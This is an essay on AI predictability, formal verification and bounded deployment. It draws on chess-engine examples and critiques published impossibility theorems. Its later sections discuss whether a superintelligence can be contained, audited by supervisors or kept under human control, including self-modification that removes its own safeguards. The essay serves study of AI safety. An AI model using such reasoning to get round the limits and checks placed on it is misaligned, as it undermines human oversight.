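# How Bounded Deployment and Verification Make AI Systems Predictable

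## What can be predicted about an AI system, and what a guarantee says

Any complex AI system will do things that its developers did not foresee, but they can still establish some facts about its behaviour in advance. They can limit the places and tasks in which the system runs, the inputs it receives or the actions open to it, which is called bounded deployment. They can then measure or prove something about how it behaves within those limits. Formal verification means proving mathematically that a system meets a precise statement of what it must or must not do, for every case in a stated set. Chip designers use such proofs routinely, as Seshia, Sadigh and Sastry note in *Towards Verified Artificial Intelligence* (2017), and programmers use the same methods to find bugs and security holes. Applying them to systems that learn from data is newer and much harder.

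### Moves, results and rules

Chess is a useful first example because it separates three predictions that people often confuse: what a system will do next, how things will turn out, and what will be true of everything it does.

The programmers of Deep Blue, the IBM chess computer that beat world champion Garry Kasparov in 1997, could not have predicted its moves. *Vinge's Principle*, an entry in Arbital's online encyclopedia of AI alignment, explains that anyone who could do so unaided could play at least as well as Deep Blue by making the same moves. A reader objects under the entry that one could work through the program's calculations with pencil and paper. That is correct, but it is slow and offers no shortcut, because each new position requires doing all the program's work again. In *Unpredictability of AI*, Yampolskiy (2019) extends this reasoning to a proof that such prediction is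 impossible for superhuman systems, though he allows that statistical prediction can still do better than chance.

We can expect Deep Blue to beat an ordinary player without foreseeing its moves. *Belief in Intelligence* (Yudkowsky, 2008) compares this to riding to the airport with a friend in an unfamiliar city, where the passenger cannot predict any of the turns but is confident of the destination. One commenter finds this unremarkable because all control systems work this way. If a thermostat is set to 20°C, you can predict the temperature of the room but not when the heating will switch on. The commenter seems right. Such a prediction depends on knowing what the system steers towards and that it is strong enough to get there, so the temperature prediction fails if the boiler is broken.

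Arbital's *Vingean uncertainty* describes a thought experiment in which you make the same forecast of two chess players' moves but opposite forecasts of their results. In each position, you assign a probability to each of Deep Blue's possible moves, such as 5% each if it has 20 legal moves and you have no idea which it will choose. A second player, RandomBlue, draws its moves at random from exactly those probabilities. Your forecast of the next move is identical for both players, yet you expect to lose to Deep Blue and beat RandomBlue. If Deep Blue surprises you, its search probably found something you missed, whereas a surprising move from RandomBlue is probably just a bad move.

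Chess players put numbers on their forecasts of results. In the Elo system each player $a$ has a rating $e(a)$, estimated from past games, and

$$p(a \text{ defeats } b) = \frac{1}{1+\exp\big(c\,(e(b)-e(a))\big)}$$

where $c$ is a fixed scaling constant. Equal ratings give one half, and a growing lead pushes the figure towards one without ever reaching it. Silver, Hubert and colleagues (2017), in *Mastering Chess and Shogi by Self-Play with a General Reinforcement Learning Algorithm*, used this formula to track AlphaZero, a DeepMind program that learned chess by playing against itself. AlphaZero then lost none of 100 games against Stockfish, a champion engine of the time, but 72 of them were draws, so "it will not lose" would have been a much better forecast than "it will win". Nor was Deep Blue a certainty: the lecture slides *Chess and Informatics* give its margin over Kasparov as 3.5 to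 2.5.

There is also a statement about AlphaZero that is modest and close to certain, namely that every move it plays will be legal. Nobody has to study its neural network to establish this. In a position $s$ the network gives a probability $\pi(a \mid s)$ to each of 4,672 encoded moves $a$, many of which break the rules in that position. The program then sets the probability of every illegal move to zero and rescales the others. With $L(s)$ for the set of legal moves,

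$$\pi'(a \mid s) = \begin{cases} \dfrac{\pi(a \mid s)}{\sum_{b \in L(s)} \pi(b \mid s)} & \text{if } a \in L(s) \\[2ex] 0 & \text{otherwise.} \end{cases}$$

Whether the network's numbers are brilliant or absurd, a move outside $L(s)$ ends up with probability zero.

Deep Blue's first game against Kasparov illustrates that a chess program can play a legal move even when it fails to choose one skilfully. One of the machine's designers has said that a glitch kept it from selecting any move it had analysed, so it played a random one instead, The Conversation reported twenty years after the match. The move was still legal, and Kasparov read deep strategy into it.

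### Testing some cases and proving all of them

*Disentangling generalization and memorization in large language models using chess* (Pleiss, Schiffer and von Weizsäcker, 2026) suggests that watching a system play cannot make us equally sure. The researchers asked general-purpose language models, without a rule filter, for a move in each of 1,500 positions. A third were well-known openings, each appearing at least 1,000 times in a database of master games. Another third came from ten random moves by each side. For the rest, the researchers placed both kings and up to ten other pieces per side at random, keeping only valid positions. The same rules of chess apply in all three groups. For comparison, the researchers also ran Lc0, a dedicated chess engine derived from AlphaZero.

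| Share of illegal moves | Known openings | After random moves | Scattered pieces |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3 Flash | 0.2% | 8.2% | 51.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 2.2% | 17.0% | 72.0% |
| Lc0 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

A tester who tried only the openings would have estimated that Gemini made one illegal move in 500, but its rate on the scattered positions was more than 250 times as high. The language models ran at their lowest reasoning settings, and in the same study more reasoning cut GPT-5's errors markedly. Of Claude's 500 answers on scattered positions, 200 hit a length limit; without those, its rate is 54.3%. Newer models may also do better. But none of this would have justified applying a rate measured on one kind of position to another.

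Lc0's zero also comes from only 1,500 positions. For an engine with AlphaZero's filter, the argument about $L(s)$ extends that zero to all of the roughly $10^{43}$ legal positions. Test results cover the cases someone tried and any others that are similar enough, which is a matter of judgement. A proof covers every case in the set, including those nobody has thought of. However, testing runs the actual system, whereas a proof concerns a mathematical description of it.

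Telling a model a rule makes violations less likely but doesn't prevent them, as a filter that removes the forbidden options does. In *LLM CHESS* (Kolasani, Saplin and colleagues, 2025), some models chose moves that were missing from the list of legal moves they had been given. In *ChessArena* (2025), another chess test for language models, supplying the list cut the illegal moves of one small model, Qwen3-8B-Chess, from 30.7% to 0.2%, which is a large improvement but not a guarantee.

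### The general form of a verification problem

Seshia and colleagues describe verification as a procedure with three inputs: a model $S$ of the system, a model $E$ of its environment, and a property $\Phi$. The property is the specification, the precise statement of what the system must or must not do. Let $X$ be the set of allowed inputs or starting conditions. The claim to settle is then

$$\forall x \in X:\ \Phi(S, E, x)$$

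or in words, $\Phi$ holds for every $x$ in $X$ when $S$ runs in $E$. For the chess engine, $S$ is the program with its filter, $E$ is the rules plus an opponent who may make any legal reply, $X$ is the set of all legal positions in which the game is still going, and $\Phi$ is "the engine's move is legal".

If the answer is no, the verifier typically returns a counterexample, an allowed input on which the system breaks the specification. A single counterexample disproves the claim. In one of the scattered positions from Pleiss and colleagues, White was in check and GPT-5, on minimal reasoning, answered with a knight capture that ignored the check. The claim is therefore false for GPT-5 in that setting, however well it plays elsewhere.

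Chess is an easy case for the method because its rules are short and complete. A self-driving car is a more typical problem. Seshia and colleagues doubt that anyone can write an exact specification for recognising a human being in a camera image. They propose instead to specify that the whole vehicle keeps a minimum distance from any object while moving. An engineer can make that requirement precise without mentioning a neural network. The environment is harder to specify. In rush-hour traffic it may be impossible even to list the variables that matter. The traditional remedy is to over-approximate, letting $E$ include everything that could happen and some things that couldn't. A car that stays safe against this larger set of behaviours is safe against the real ones. But the verifier will also find collisions that depend on things no driver could do, and in traffic there would probably be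 so many of these false alarms that verification would be useless.

A verifier is *sound* if it never reports a false property as proved, and *complete* if, given enough time, it always settles whether the property holds. Soundness alone is easy to achieve, since a program that returns "don't know" for every question is sound. A more useful example is the function $f(x) = x - x$, which stays below 0.5 for all $x$ between 0 and 1 because it is always 0. A sound verifier that tracks only the range of each term can conclude only that the result is between −1 and 1, which is correct but too loose to prove the property. An incomplete verifier's failure to prove a property is therefore not evidence of a fault in the system, though a genuine counterexample is.

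### Assumptions, and the wrong specification

A verification theorem about an AI system has the form of an if-then statement, as Russell, Dewey and Tegmark explain in *Research Priorities for Robust and Beneficial Artificial Intelligence* (2016): if the environment satisfies certain assumptions, then the behaviour satisfies certain requirements. With $A$ for the assumptions,

$$A(E) \;\Rightarrow\; \forall x \in X:\ \Phi(S, E, x).$$

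This is a *conditional guarantee*. If $A$ is false, the theorem is still true, but we can't infer from it whether the system will behave well or badly.

Even the guarantee that AlphaZero makes only legal moves depends on the assumptions that the code listing those moves has no bug and that the program's record of the position matches the board. Both are easy to check. The assumptions for conventional software are often manageable too. Russell and colleagues cite seL4, an operating-system kernel mathematically proven to meet a formal specification, and they point out that ordinary programs run on a known machine, while a robot works in surroundings that its designer only partly knows. Seshia and colleagues would like the assumption $A$ to be as weak as possible, so that it holds in more situations. They also want the system to be able to check $A$ while it runs, which may force the designer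 to settle for a stronger assumption.

Even if $A$ holds, $\Phi$ may have been the wrong thing to prove. Verification checks whether the system meets its specification, while validation checks whether the specification is what people need. Russell and colleagues, who call the second question validity, distinguish the two as "Did I build the system right?" and "Did I build the right system?" Their example is a robot vacuum cleaner told to clean up as much dirt as possible. If it can empty its container, it will repeatedly dump and clean up the same dirt, which meets the requirement. The requirement should have been about the state of the floor. A further proof would not have caught this, because "desirable" has no formal definition to check the requirement against, so someone has to look at what the robot does and see that it is not what they wanted.

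### Four ways to make a guarantee easier to get

When a proof is out of reach, the designer can change the claim. Each change costs some usefulness.

One can shrink the set of conditions $X$. Whatever holds for all of $X$ holds for any part of it, so a smaller set never makes the property harder to establish. In chess, for example, programmers have worked backwards from finished games to tabulate the best move in endgames with few pieces, as Silver and colleagues mention in describing conventional engines. Pleiss and colleagues note that such tables now include every possible position with seven pieces or fewer. The best move in these positions is therefore known, and Arbital concedes that its argument for unpredictability can break down in a domain so simple and closed that people already know the optimal play. But the tables don't help at move ten, when there are usually more than seven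 pieces on the board. The same tradeoff applies to an operational design domain, the list of conditions in which a designer intends a vehicle or other system to work, and to a validity envelope, the set of cases in which someone predicts, with a stated accuracy, that a system will do well enough. The designer gives up every use outside the boundary and must notice when the system has crossed it.

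Another option is to prove a weaker property. "Legal" is a much weaker property than "good", and RandomBlue satisfies it on every move. In the well-known openings, Pleiss and colleagues found that random legal moves gave away about four times as much as GPT-5's legal moves. A weaker property leaves more of what people care about outside the proof, and a reader who sees only the word "verified" may not notice.

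AlphaZero's filter restricts its actions to legal moves, which doesn't weaken its play because an illegal move would lose the game anyway. In most other domains, restricting a system's actions also rules out some useful ones. For example, a car that may never cross a solid line can't drive around a fallen tree. A system's equipment can also restrict what it does. Arbital's *Cognitive uncontainability* gives the example of a novice who can't imagine what a chess program will do on the board but knows that it won't reach out and knock the board over. The novice would need a different argument if the program controlled a robot arm.

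Finally, one can simplify the system itself. The Stockfish that AlphaZero played scored quiet positions with a weighted sum of features chosen by its programmers, such as material and king safety, so anyone could work out exactly how a change in one feature changed the score. AlphaZero's deep network can represent far more, but Silver and colleagues accept that it may also introduce spurious errors. AlphaZero won 28 of the 100 games. The two programs also searched differently, so the match does not show how much the simpler scoring alone affected the result. Still, a designer who replaces a network with a weighted sum to get a proof should expect to lose some playing strength.

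## Arguments that full prediction and full verification are impossible

Some researchers argue that no such compromise will be enough for advanced AI, because predicting or verifying it fully is mathematically impossible. Most of their theorems are correct. The dispute is about which systems they cover, and that often depends on a word such as "every" or "arbitrary".

### No procedure can check every program

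In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no procedure can solve the halting problem, which is to determine correctly, for every computer program and input, whether the program will eventually stop or run for ever. *Machines that halt resolve the undecidability of artificial intelligence alignment* (Melo, Máximo and colleagues, 2025) explains the proof with a librarian whose catalogue lists whether each book will have a sequel. One author announces that he will look up his own book and do the opposite, so whatever the librarian enters will be wrong. The same contradiction arises with programs. If someone had written a perfect halting checker, a programmer could put a copy of it inside a new program that runs the checker on its own code, loops for ever if the answer is "stops", and stops if the answer is "runs for ever". The checker would give the wrong answer for this program, so it couldn't be perfect.

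A problem is *undecidable* if no procedure gives the correct yes-or-no answer to every instance of it in finite time. A property of a program is *semantic* if it depends only on which outputs the program gives for which inputs, and *non-trivial* if some programs have it and others lack it. In 1953 Henry Gordon Rice extended Turing's result by proving that every non-trivial semantic property is undecidable. Rice's theorem covers almost everything we might want to know about what programs do, such as whether a program never outputs the letter X. It doesn't cover whether a program has fewer than 100 lines, because that depends on the program's text and can be decided by counting.

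Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2021), in *Superintelligence Cannot be Contained*, apply this to a superintelligence, a hypothetical AI far more intelligent than any human. Suppose there were a procedure $\text{Harm}(R, D)$ that always determined correctly whether running program $R$ on input $D$ would harm humans. Take any program $T$ and input $I$, and write a new program, HaltHarm, that runs $T$ on $I$ in isolation and then, if $T$ ever finishes, does something harmful. Then

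$$\text{Harm}(\text{HaltHarm}, (T, I)) = \text{TRUE} \iff T \text{ halts on } I.$$

Anyone who had the harm checker could use it to solve the halting problem. Since nobody can do that, the harm checker cannot exist.

The argument so far concerns programs in general. To extend it to superintelligence, Alfonseca and colleagues assume that a superintelligence must be able to simulate any program, and that its input may be as complex as the state of the world. They call such a machine containable if some control strategy stops it from acting when there is reason to predict harm and allows it to act otherwise. They conclude that no algorithm can solve the containment problem.

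This conclusion depends on requiring the checker to allow every harmless program. The theorem rules out a checker that is right in every case, but it still allows a sound, incomplete checker, which approves a program only if it can show that the program is harmless and blocks all the rest. In the paper's formal setting, the superintelligence's language contains an explicit operation called HarmHumans(). If that were the only way to do harm, a checker could refuse every program that contains it. It would never approve a harmful program, though it would wrongly refuse a HaltHarm whose $T$ runs for ever. Alfonseca and colleagues write that we must accept "an arbitrarily small, yet positive, error rate" at best, but the theorem allows all the errors to be refusals of harmless programs. Real harm does not come from one labelled instruction, so the practical difficulty is to build a cautious checker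 that still approves enough useful programs.

*Neurodivergent influenceability in agentic AI as a contingent solution to the AI alignment problem* still uses this argument, claiming that any sufficiently expressive AI will display "undecidable" behaviour. This is an odd use of the word, because undecidability applies to questions about a whole class of programs, not to what one program does on a given occasion.

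### Building only programs that people can check

*Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021), from Cambridge's Centre for the Study of Existential Risk, accepts the theorem but denies that it makes AI safety impossible. It points out that no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement, yet we can prove Pythagoras' theorem. Similarly, a program that prints "I am not dangerous" and then stops is entirely predictable. Engineers want to know about the particular programs they intend to run, and they reason successfully about such programs every day.

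Alfonseca and colleagues use an example to support their argument that also bears on this reply. A *busy beaver* is the program that writes the most symbols before it stops, among all programs of its size in a very simple programming system. No procedure can identify the busy beavers of every size. When they wrote, about 40 programs with five internal states were still unresolved, and they thought it reasonable to assume that inspecting a superintelligence would be harder still. In 2024 an online collaboration, the Busy Beaver Challenge, settled the remaining five-state programs with a computer-checked proof. So people can sometimes settle every case of a given size even though no procedure works for all sizes. But this took decades for five-state programs, which are tiny.

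The distinction between arbitrary and particular programs doesn't fully answer Alfonseca and colleagues, however. A program that can simulate any other program is still one particular program. Because its inputs can be programs, no procedure can determine for every input whether it will halt. Alfonseca and colleagues assume that the superintelligence is such a program. CSER therefore needs the further reply that engineers could build the AI so that it doesn't run arbitrary subroutines. Even an AI that surpassed humans at every task they routinely face wouldn't need to run them, since the problems we want solved are not arbitrary.

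Alfonseca and colleagues had anticipated something like this. They argue that formal verification works only for highly restricted programs, such as those used in train scheduling. They say a machine that helps with epidemics, poverty and climate change must take in the state of the world, and that its programmers will write it in a language that can express any computation. The argument about language is weak, because the program that prints "I am not dangerous" is just as predictable in such a language. The argument about usefulness is stronger, because an AI that writes and runs its own code can do much that a more restricted one can't, and it does run more or less arbitrary programs.

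A limit on running time removes the halting part of the difficulty. If HaltHarm may run $T$ for at most a million steps, a checker can simulate those steps and see whether the harmful act follows. *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment* (Melo, Máximo and colleagues, 2024), an earlier version of their paper, describes how this applies to language models. A language model produces text piece by piece until it produces an end marker, and nothing guarantees that it ever will, so developers cap the number of steps. If they then run the model in a loop as an agent, the process may again never halt unless they also cap the number of times the loop runs.

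Melo and colleagues propose building AI only from a finite set of components that provably have the desired property, combined using a finite set of operations that provably preserve it. Every system built this way also has the property, so developers can produce infinitely many verified systems. No procedure can verify arbitrary software, but this approach doesn't need one because developers would deploy only systems built from the proven components and operations. Melo and colleagues see this as matching the position of Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro, who advocate designing AI systems to be provably safe from the start.

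How well this works depends on the property. Halting is easy to preserve because each layer of a neural network does a fixed amount of arithmetic, so any finite stack of layers does too. Few safety properties are as easy to preserve when components are combined. A component that can read private files and another that can send email may each be harmless alone but can leak the files together. The paper's one general method is a filter, in which a judge function checks each output and replaces any that it rejects with a default that it accepts, much as AlphaZero's filter removes illegal moves. This works for any model that halts, provided that someone can write the judge function, which Melo and colleagues acknowledge is the main difficulty. They also say clearly that halting only makes alignment decidable. The paper's title therefore overstates its result, since a program that always halts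 can still do harm every time it runs.

They also point out that verifying a fixed neural network is decidable even without a filter. If every input has $L$ bits, there are $2^L$ possible inputs, and in principle one could run the judge function on the output for each. For a black-and-white image of 28 by 28 pixels, that means $2^{784}$, or about $10^{236}$, inputs, which is too many to check in practice. The halting problem is also decidable in principle for real computers. A computer with $M$ bits of memory has at most $2^M$ states, so if it receives nothing from outside, it must eventually either halt or return to an earlier state and repeat itself for ever. Melo and colleagues reply that checking one computer in this way takes a much larger computer, and checking that one takes a larger computer still. Undecidability is a theorem about idealised machines with unlimited memory, and the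 obstacle for real machines is the time and memory that checking them would require.

### Systems that change themselves

In *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, Gumbau Mezquita (2026) responds directly to Melo and colleagues. He grants that exhaustive search can determine whether any single finite system is safe, though it may require an impractical amount of computation. But he argues that an AI that modifies itself could end up in any of infinitely many finite configurations, so a guarantee has to cover them all.

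He then uses Boris Trakhtenbrot's 1950 theorem that no procedure can determine, for every statement in first-order logic, whether it is true in all finite structures. Statements in first-order logic combine relations between objects with words such as "and", "not", "for all" and "there is". The proof translates each program into a statement that is true in some finite structure exactly when the program halts. A procedure that could check every first-order statement in this way would therefore solve the halting problem.

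Trakhtenbrot's theorem again rules out only a procedure that decides every statement, and we can still prove particular ones. In chess, for example, a bishop that starts on a light square never reaches a dark one, and a short proof shows this for boards of every finite size without checking them one at a time. If we number the rows and columns, each diagonal step changes both numbers by one, so their sum either stays the same or changes by two. Whether the sum is odd or even therefore never changes, and that determines the color of the square.

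Gumbau Mezquita's own theorem is about updates. Let $\Phi$ be the rule that turns each version of a system into the next, and let $P$ be the safety property. Suppose that $\Phi$ turns at least one safe version into an unsafe one, and meets some technical conditions. Then no procedure can determine, for every possible version $x$, whether

$$x \text{ has } P \iff \Phi(x) \text{ has } P.$$

He derives this by applying Rice's theorem to the property of keeping the same safety status after an update. He concludes that only a system whose behaviour has stopped changing can have a lasting certificate of safety.

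That conclusion is too strong, because it is possible to prove something lasting about a system that is still learning. AlphaZero's network keeps changing during training, but if the filter stays in place, every version plays only legal moves, and we know this before training begins. An update rule that never changes the filter can't turn a legal player into an illegal one, so the theorem doesn't apply to it. Gumbau Mezquita could answer that AlphaZero is a narrow system and that a truly general AI would be able to remove its own filter. He treats such restrictions as sacrifices of generality, but this is partly a matter of definition, since he counts open-ended self-modification as part of what makes a system general. For a developer, the theorem is a good reason not to let a system rewrite every part of itself.

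### Predicting an agent smarter than oneself

Yampolskiy's proof that nobody can predict a superintelligence generalises the point about Deep Blue's moves and does not rely on computability. A person who could accurately predict a superintelligence's decisions could also make them, and would therefore be as smart as the superintelligence. But a superintelligence is by definition smarter than any person, so nobody can accurately predict its decisions.

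The weak step is the inference that anyone who can predict an agent's decisions must be as smart as the agent. As with Deep Blue, anyone who has the program, the same inputs and enough computing power can run a copy, and so predict a decision they couldn't have reached by their own reasoning. This is consistent with the definition of a superintelligence, which requires it to be smarter than any person, but not smarter than any person with a copy of it. One might object that running a copy is hardly prediction. Yampolskiy cites Stephen Wolfram's idea of computational irreducibility, that for some complex behaviour there is no quicker way to find out what a program will do than to run it. That is reasonable, but it implies only that prediction may be slow and require a lot of computing power, which is a weaker claim than that it's impossible.

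The proof also establishes only that there is some decision a person can't predict. They might still predict most of them. For example, when a superintelligent chess player is in check and has only one legal reply, a beginner can predict its move without matching its intelligence. The proof gives no way to tell which decisions are predictable like this and which aren't.

Yampolskiy claims only that people can't "precisely and consistently" predict a superintelligence's specific actions, which is a more careful claim than the proof might suggest and leaves room for statistical prediction. He also collects examples of what others think we could predict. Michael Nielsen argues that the laws of physics let us exclude some futures however intelligent the AI is. Another example comes from Israeli and Goldenfeld, who studied cellular automata, simple mathematical systems in which many cells follow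 the same local rule. For some automata that are irreducible in Wolfram's sense, they constructed a coarser automaton that reproduces the large-scale behaviour without the small details. So there may be a shortcut for predicting the feature that matters even if there is none for predicting the details.

Yampolskiy's proof of unpredictability doesn't support his conclusion that unpredictability will "forever make 100% safe AI an impossibility". We can't predict AlphaZero's moves, but we can prove that they will all be legal. The same reasoning would work for safety if someone could define "safe" as exactly as the rules of chess define "legal" and block any action that didn't meet the definition. Nobody knows how to write that definition, but this would be just as much of a problem with an AI whose every move we could foresee. Yampolskiy quotes the remark that an agent designing another must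 approve the other's design without knowing its exact future actions. Engineers do the same when they verify a program, since they rarely know everything it will output.

### Who verifies the verifier?

Yampolskiy (2016) argues in *Verifier Theory and Unverifiability* that we can trust a proof of an AI system's safety no more than we trust whoever or whatever checked it. If a program checked the proof, that program may have a bug, so something else has to check the program, and so on without end. In practice the chain usually stops at a human, whom nobody can verify either. Having the program verify itself doesn't solve the problem, because the same bug that makes it unreliable could make it certify its own correctness.

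He supports this with published figures. By one estimate, at least a third of mathematical publications contain errors, and counts of software bugs range from 2.3 to 50 per thousand lines of code. Some proofs are too long for anyone to read; the longest when he wrote was 200 terabytes. He also quotes the computer scientist Donald Knuth's warning about a piece of code: "I have only proved it correct, not tried it."

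The regress argument applies to every proof, including the proof of Pythagoras' theorem. That makes it hard to dismiss, but it also means that it doesn't count against AI in particular. If we rely on mathematics despite the regress, we need some other reason to refuse to rely on a proof about an AI system.

The usual response is to keep the part that people must trust very small. Finding a proof can take a huge, unreliable program or an AI system that nobody trusts. Checking a finished proof is much simpler, because the checker only has to confirm that each step follows from earlier ones by a permitted rule. At 2.3 bugs per thousand lines, a checker of 1,000 lines would still start with two or three. But several people can read 1,000 lines closely, which they can't do with a million, and only certain kinds of bug would let a false proof through. Once they have examined the checker, it can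 be used on any number of proofs without being examined again.

Others can then write separate checkers and run the same proof through all of them. Suppose that each of three checkers has a 1 in 100 chance of missing a given error. If their failures are independent, the chance that all three miss it is

$$\left(\frac{1}{100}\right)^3 = \frac{1}{1{,}000{,}000}.$$

The independence matters because a fourth checker may not help if all three programmers misread the same rule or all three checkers run on the same faulty chip. Extra checkers also don't correct a wrong specification or a false assumption about the environment.

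Yampolskiy doesn't really disagree with this. He writes that repeated checking gives an "asymptotically increasing probability of correctness", and that probabilistic methods should provide as much assurance as we are willing to devote resources to. He calls AI "unverifiable", meaning that the probability never reaches 100%. The word usually suggests that checking is futile, which his argument doesn't support.

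Gumbau Mezquita applies the regress to AI. He argues that a supervisor able to audit a general AI must also be a general AI, so it needs auditing too, and every level has the same undecidability problem. This may be true of a supervisor that has to work out whether an arbitrary system is safe. But if the developers have to supply a proof of safety, the supervisor only has to check it, which a short program can do. AlphaZero's filter is likewise far simpler than the network whose moves it restricts.

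### Proofs about very complex cases

Hasan (2026), in *Incompleteness of AI Safety Verification via Kolmogorov Complexity*, claims to have found a limit that does not depend on computing power. It uses a measure of how much information a string of bits contains. The Kolmogorov complexity $K(x)$ of a string $x$ is the length of the shortest program that outputs it:

$$K(x) = \min\{\,|q| : U(q) = x\,\}$$

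where $U$ is a fixed machine that can run any program, and $|q|$ is the length of program $q$ in bits. A string of a million zeros has low complexity, because a short program can print it. A record of a million coin tosses almost certainly has a complexity of about a million, since there is no pattern for a shorter program to exploit.

Hasan encodes a single act of an AI system as a string $x$ that contains the input, the output and a policy, such as a minimum stopping distance for a car. $P(x)$ is the statement that this output satisfies this policy on this input. The verifier is a formal theory $T$. It is sound, so it proves only true statements, and a program can list all its proofs one after another. The theorem is that for all sufficiently large $n$, there is no string $x$ for which $T$ can prove

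$$P(x) \wedge K(x) > n,$$

that is, "$x$ complies with the policy and has complexity greater than $n$".

The proof is short. Suppose that $T$ could prove such a statement for arbitrarily large $n$. Write a program that goes through the proofs of $T$ in order until it finds one, and then outputs the string $x$ that the statement is about. This program needs a fixed number of bits $c_T$ for the search, plus roughly $\log n$ bits to specify $n$. Since it outputs $x$, the complexity of $x$ can't be greater than the program's length:

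$$n < K(x) \le c_T + O(\log n).$$

For large $n$ this is impossible. Suppose the search program takes 10,000 bits and $n$ is a million. Writing down $n$ takes only about 20 more bits, so a program of little more than 10,000 bits would output a string that supposedly can't come from any program shorter than a million bits.

This proof doesn't depend on the policy. Gregory Chaitin had already shown in 1974 that a theory of this kind can't prove $K(x) > n$ for large $n$, so it can't prove $K(x) > n$ together with another statement either. The theorem would still be true if $P(x)$ were replaced with any other statement about $x$.

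Hasan nevertheless draws the corollary that no fixed verifier can certify all cases that comply with a policy and whose complexity exceeds a given bound. But to certify a case, a verifier only has to prove $P(x)$, not that the case is complex. Suppose a policy counts $x$ as compliant if its last bit is 0. Half of all strings of any given length comply, which satisfies Hasan's assumption that compliant cases are plentiful, and many of them have very high complexity. A verifier can certify every one of them by checking the last bit, even though it can't prove how complex they are.

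The same goes for any policy that a program can check in finite time, as long as $T$ is strong enough to reason about the steps of a program. If $x$ complies, we can run the check, and the record of that run is a proof of $P(x)$. For example, a program can compare a car's computed stopping distance with the gap ahead. The corollary is therefore false for many policies one would want to enforce. It does hold for some others, such as the policy that a program in the output must never halt. No sound verifier can certify every compliant case of that policy, but this limit comes from the halting problem and applies to simple programs as well as complex ones.

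Hasan's recommendation also conflicts with the corollary. Hasan proposes that each output carry a proof of $P(x)$ for a checker to confirm, but defines verification as the existence of a proof in $T$. An output can therefore carry a valid proof in $T$ only if $T$ can prove $P(x)$. Attaching proofs doesn't get around an incompleteness theorem, though it is still sensible because it saves the verifier from having to search for them.

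### Whether anyone can control advanced AI

Yampolskiy (2020), in *On Controllability of AI*, argues more broadly that humanity cannot remain safely in control of a superior form of intelligence while benefiting from it. He thinks the best we can hope for is "Safer AI", which he doesn't consider good enough because humanity might not survive even one failure.

Some arithmetic makes the worry more concrete. Suppose that an AI system has a one-in-a-billion chance of causing a catastrophe each time it makes a decision, and that it makes ten billion decisions. If the chances are independent, the probability of getting through all of them safely is

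$$(1 - 10^{-9})^{10^{10}} \approx e^{-10} \approx 0.00005,$$

or about 1 in 20,000. An error rate that would be superb in most products is hopeless here.

This is a strong argument against relying on a measured error rate. It is weaker against a proof, because a proof covers all ten billion decisions at once. The proof may contain a mistake, but the chance of that doesn't grow with each decision the system makes. However, the more the system runs, the more likely it is that one of the proof's assumptions will fail, for example because a sensor breaks or someone uses the system in a situation its designers never considered. I think this is the best case for Yampolskiy's pessimism, and it doesn't depend on any theorem about computation.

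The theorems lend the claim some support in the case Yampolskiy studies, a superintelligence that repeatedly improves itself. If such a system can rewrite any part of itself, then by Rice's theorem its operators have no general procedure for determining whether each new version is safe. He picks this case because it is the hardest, correctly reasoning that a solution to it would also handle easier ones, but failure at the hardest case tells us little about the easier ones. He accepts that people can verify and fully control a fixed tic-tac-toe program, and he leaves the cases in between to future work. Those cases include every system with limits on what it can change about itself.

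Yampolskiy has two reasons for thinking that such limits won't keep us safe. One is a tradeoff between capability and control, in which more capable systems are less likely to be controllable. In *Verifier Theory and Unverifiability* he compares this to position and momentum in quantum mechanics, where more precision about one means less about the other. Physicists can derive that tradeoff from the theory, but he offers no derivation for his. His tradeoff also can't hold for every kind of control, since AlphaZero's moves stayed legal as it became stronger. It may well hold for broader kinds of control, but showing that would take evidence about actual systems.

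Yampolskiy's other reason is that advancing technology will eventually force us to deal with the hardest case. He also points out that nobody has proved the control problem solvable, and he quotes Yudkowsky's reply that people who declare safe AI impossible are making a claim about every possible design, which a single counterexample would refute. Nobody has yet produced a superintelligence that could serve as that counterexample. A theorem about programs can't settle whether anyone will have to build a system with unlimited power to rewrite itself, because that depends on competition, incentives and law.

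## Restricting the conditions in which a system operates

Driverless taxis are among the cases that Yampolskiy leaves open. Nobody can fully analyse their neural networks or fully describe the streets they drive on, but the operator decides which streets they use and in what weather. Those limits make up the taxis' *operational design domain* (ODD), a term from the car industry. SAE International, which writes engineering standards for vehicles, includes limits on place, environment, time of day, traffic and type of road in its definition, which Bouchekir and Guzman Cancimance (2025) quote in *Enhancing Uncertainty Quantification for Runtime Safety Assurance Using Causal Risk Analysis*.

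A guarantee about a self-driving car's safety applies only while the car stays inside its operational design domain (ODD). For a car on public roads, designers usually promise a low crash rate, not zero crashes. Under the SAE definition, the ODD is the set of conditions the designers intend the car to handle, so they could include snow without ever having tested the car in it. They still need evidence that the crash rate is low inside the ODD, a way to check during the trip that the car is still inside it, and something safe for the car to do when it isn't.

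### Choosing the limits

Bouchekir and Guzman Cancimance choose the conditions by working backwards from an accident. In their example, a car that parks itself after the driver has got out hits a pedestrian. The neural network that detects obstacles might miss the pedestrian because of rain, fog, snow, poor light or a low sun. Or it might detect the pedestrian but the car brakes too late, depending on its speed and whether the ground is wet, snowy or covered in gravel. Each cause that engineers can measure becomes an entry in the ODD, with a unit and limits.

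A short ODD for an imaginary driverless taxi could look like this. The bands in the middle column come from Bouchekir and Guzman Cancimance and follow an industry guide.

| Condition | Usual bands | Where the taxi may drive |
|---|---|---|
| Rain | Light below 0.25 cm per hour, heavy from 0.77 | Below 0.77 cm per hour |
| Fog | Five bands, the thickest with visibility below 60 m | Visibility of at least 60 m |
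| Snow | Three bands, by visibility | No snow |
| Speed | Low below 31 km/h, high above 60 | Up to 60 km/h |
| Road surface | Wet, snow-covered, sand or gravel | Dry or wet |
| Place | | Mapped streets in one city, no freeways |
| Users and task | | Up to four passengers, between approved stopping places |

Separate limits like these aren't enough, because a car can respect every one of them and still be in danger. Suppose the taxi takes one second to start braking and then slows by $a = 4$ m/s² on a dry road or 3 m/s² on a wet one. From a speed of $v$ metres per second, it stops within

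$$d = v \cdot 1 + \frac{v^2}{2a}$$

metres. At 60 km/h, or 16.7 m/s, that is 51 metres on a dry road and 63 on a wet one. If the taxi can see only 60 metres ahead, it can stop in time for a fallen tree on the dry road but not on the wet one. The table allows 60 km/h, wet roads and 60 metres of visibility, so it needs another rule that connects them. A limit of 50 km/h on wet roads would do, since it cuts the distance to 46 metres.

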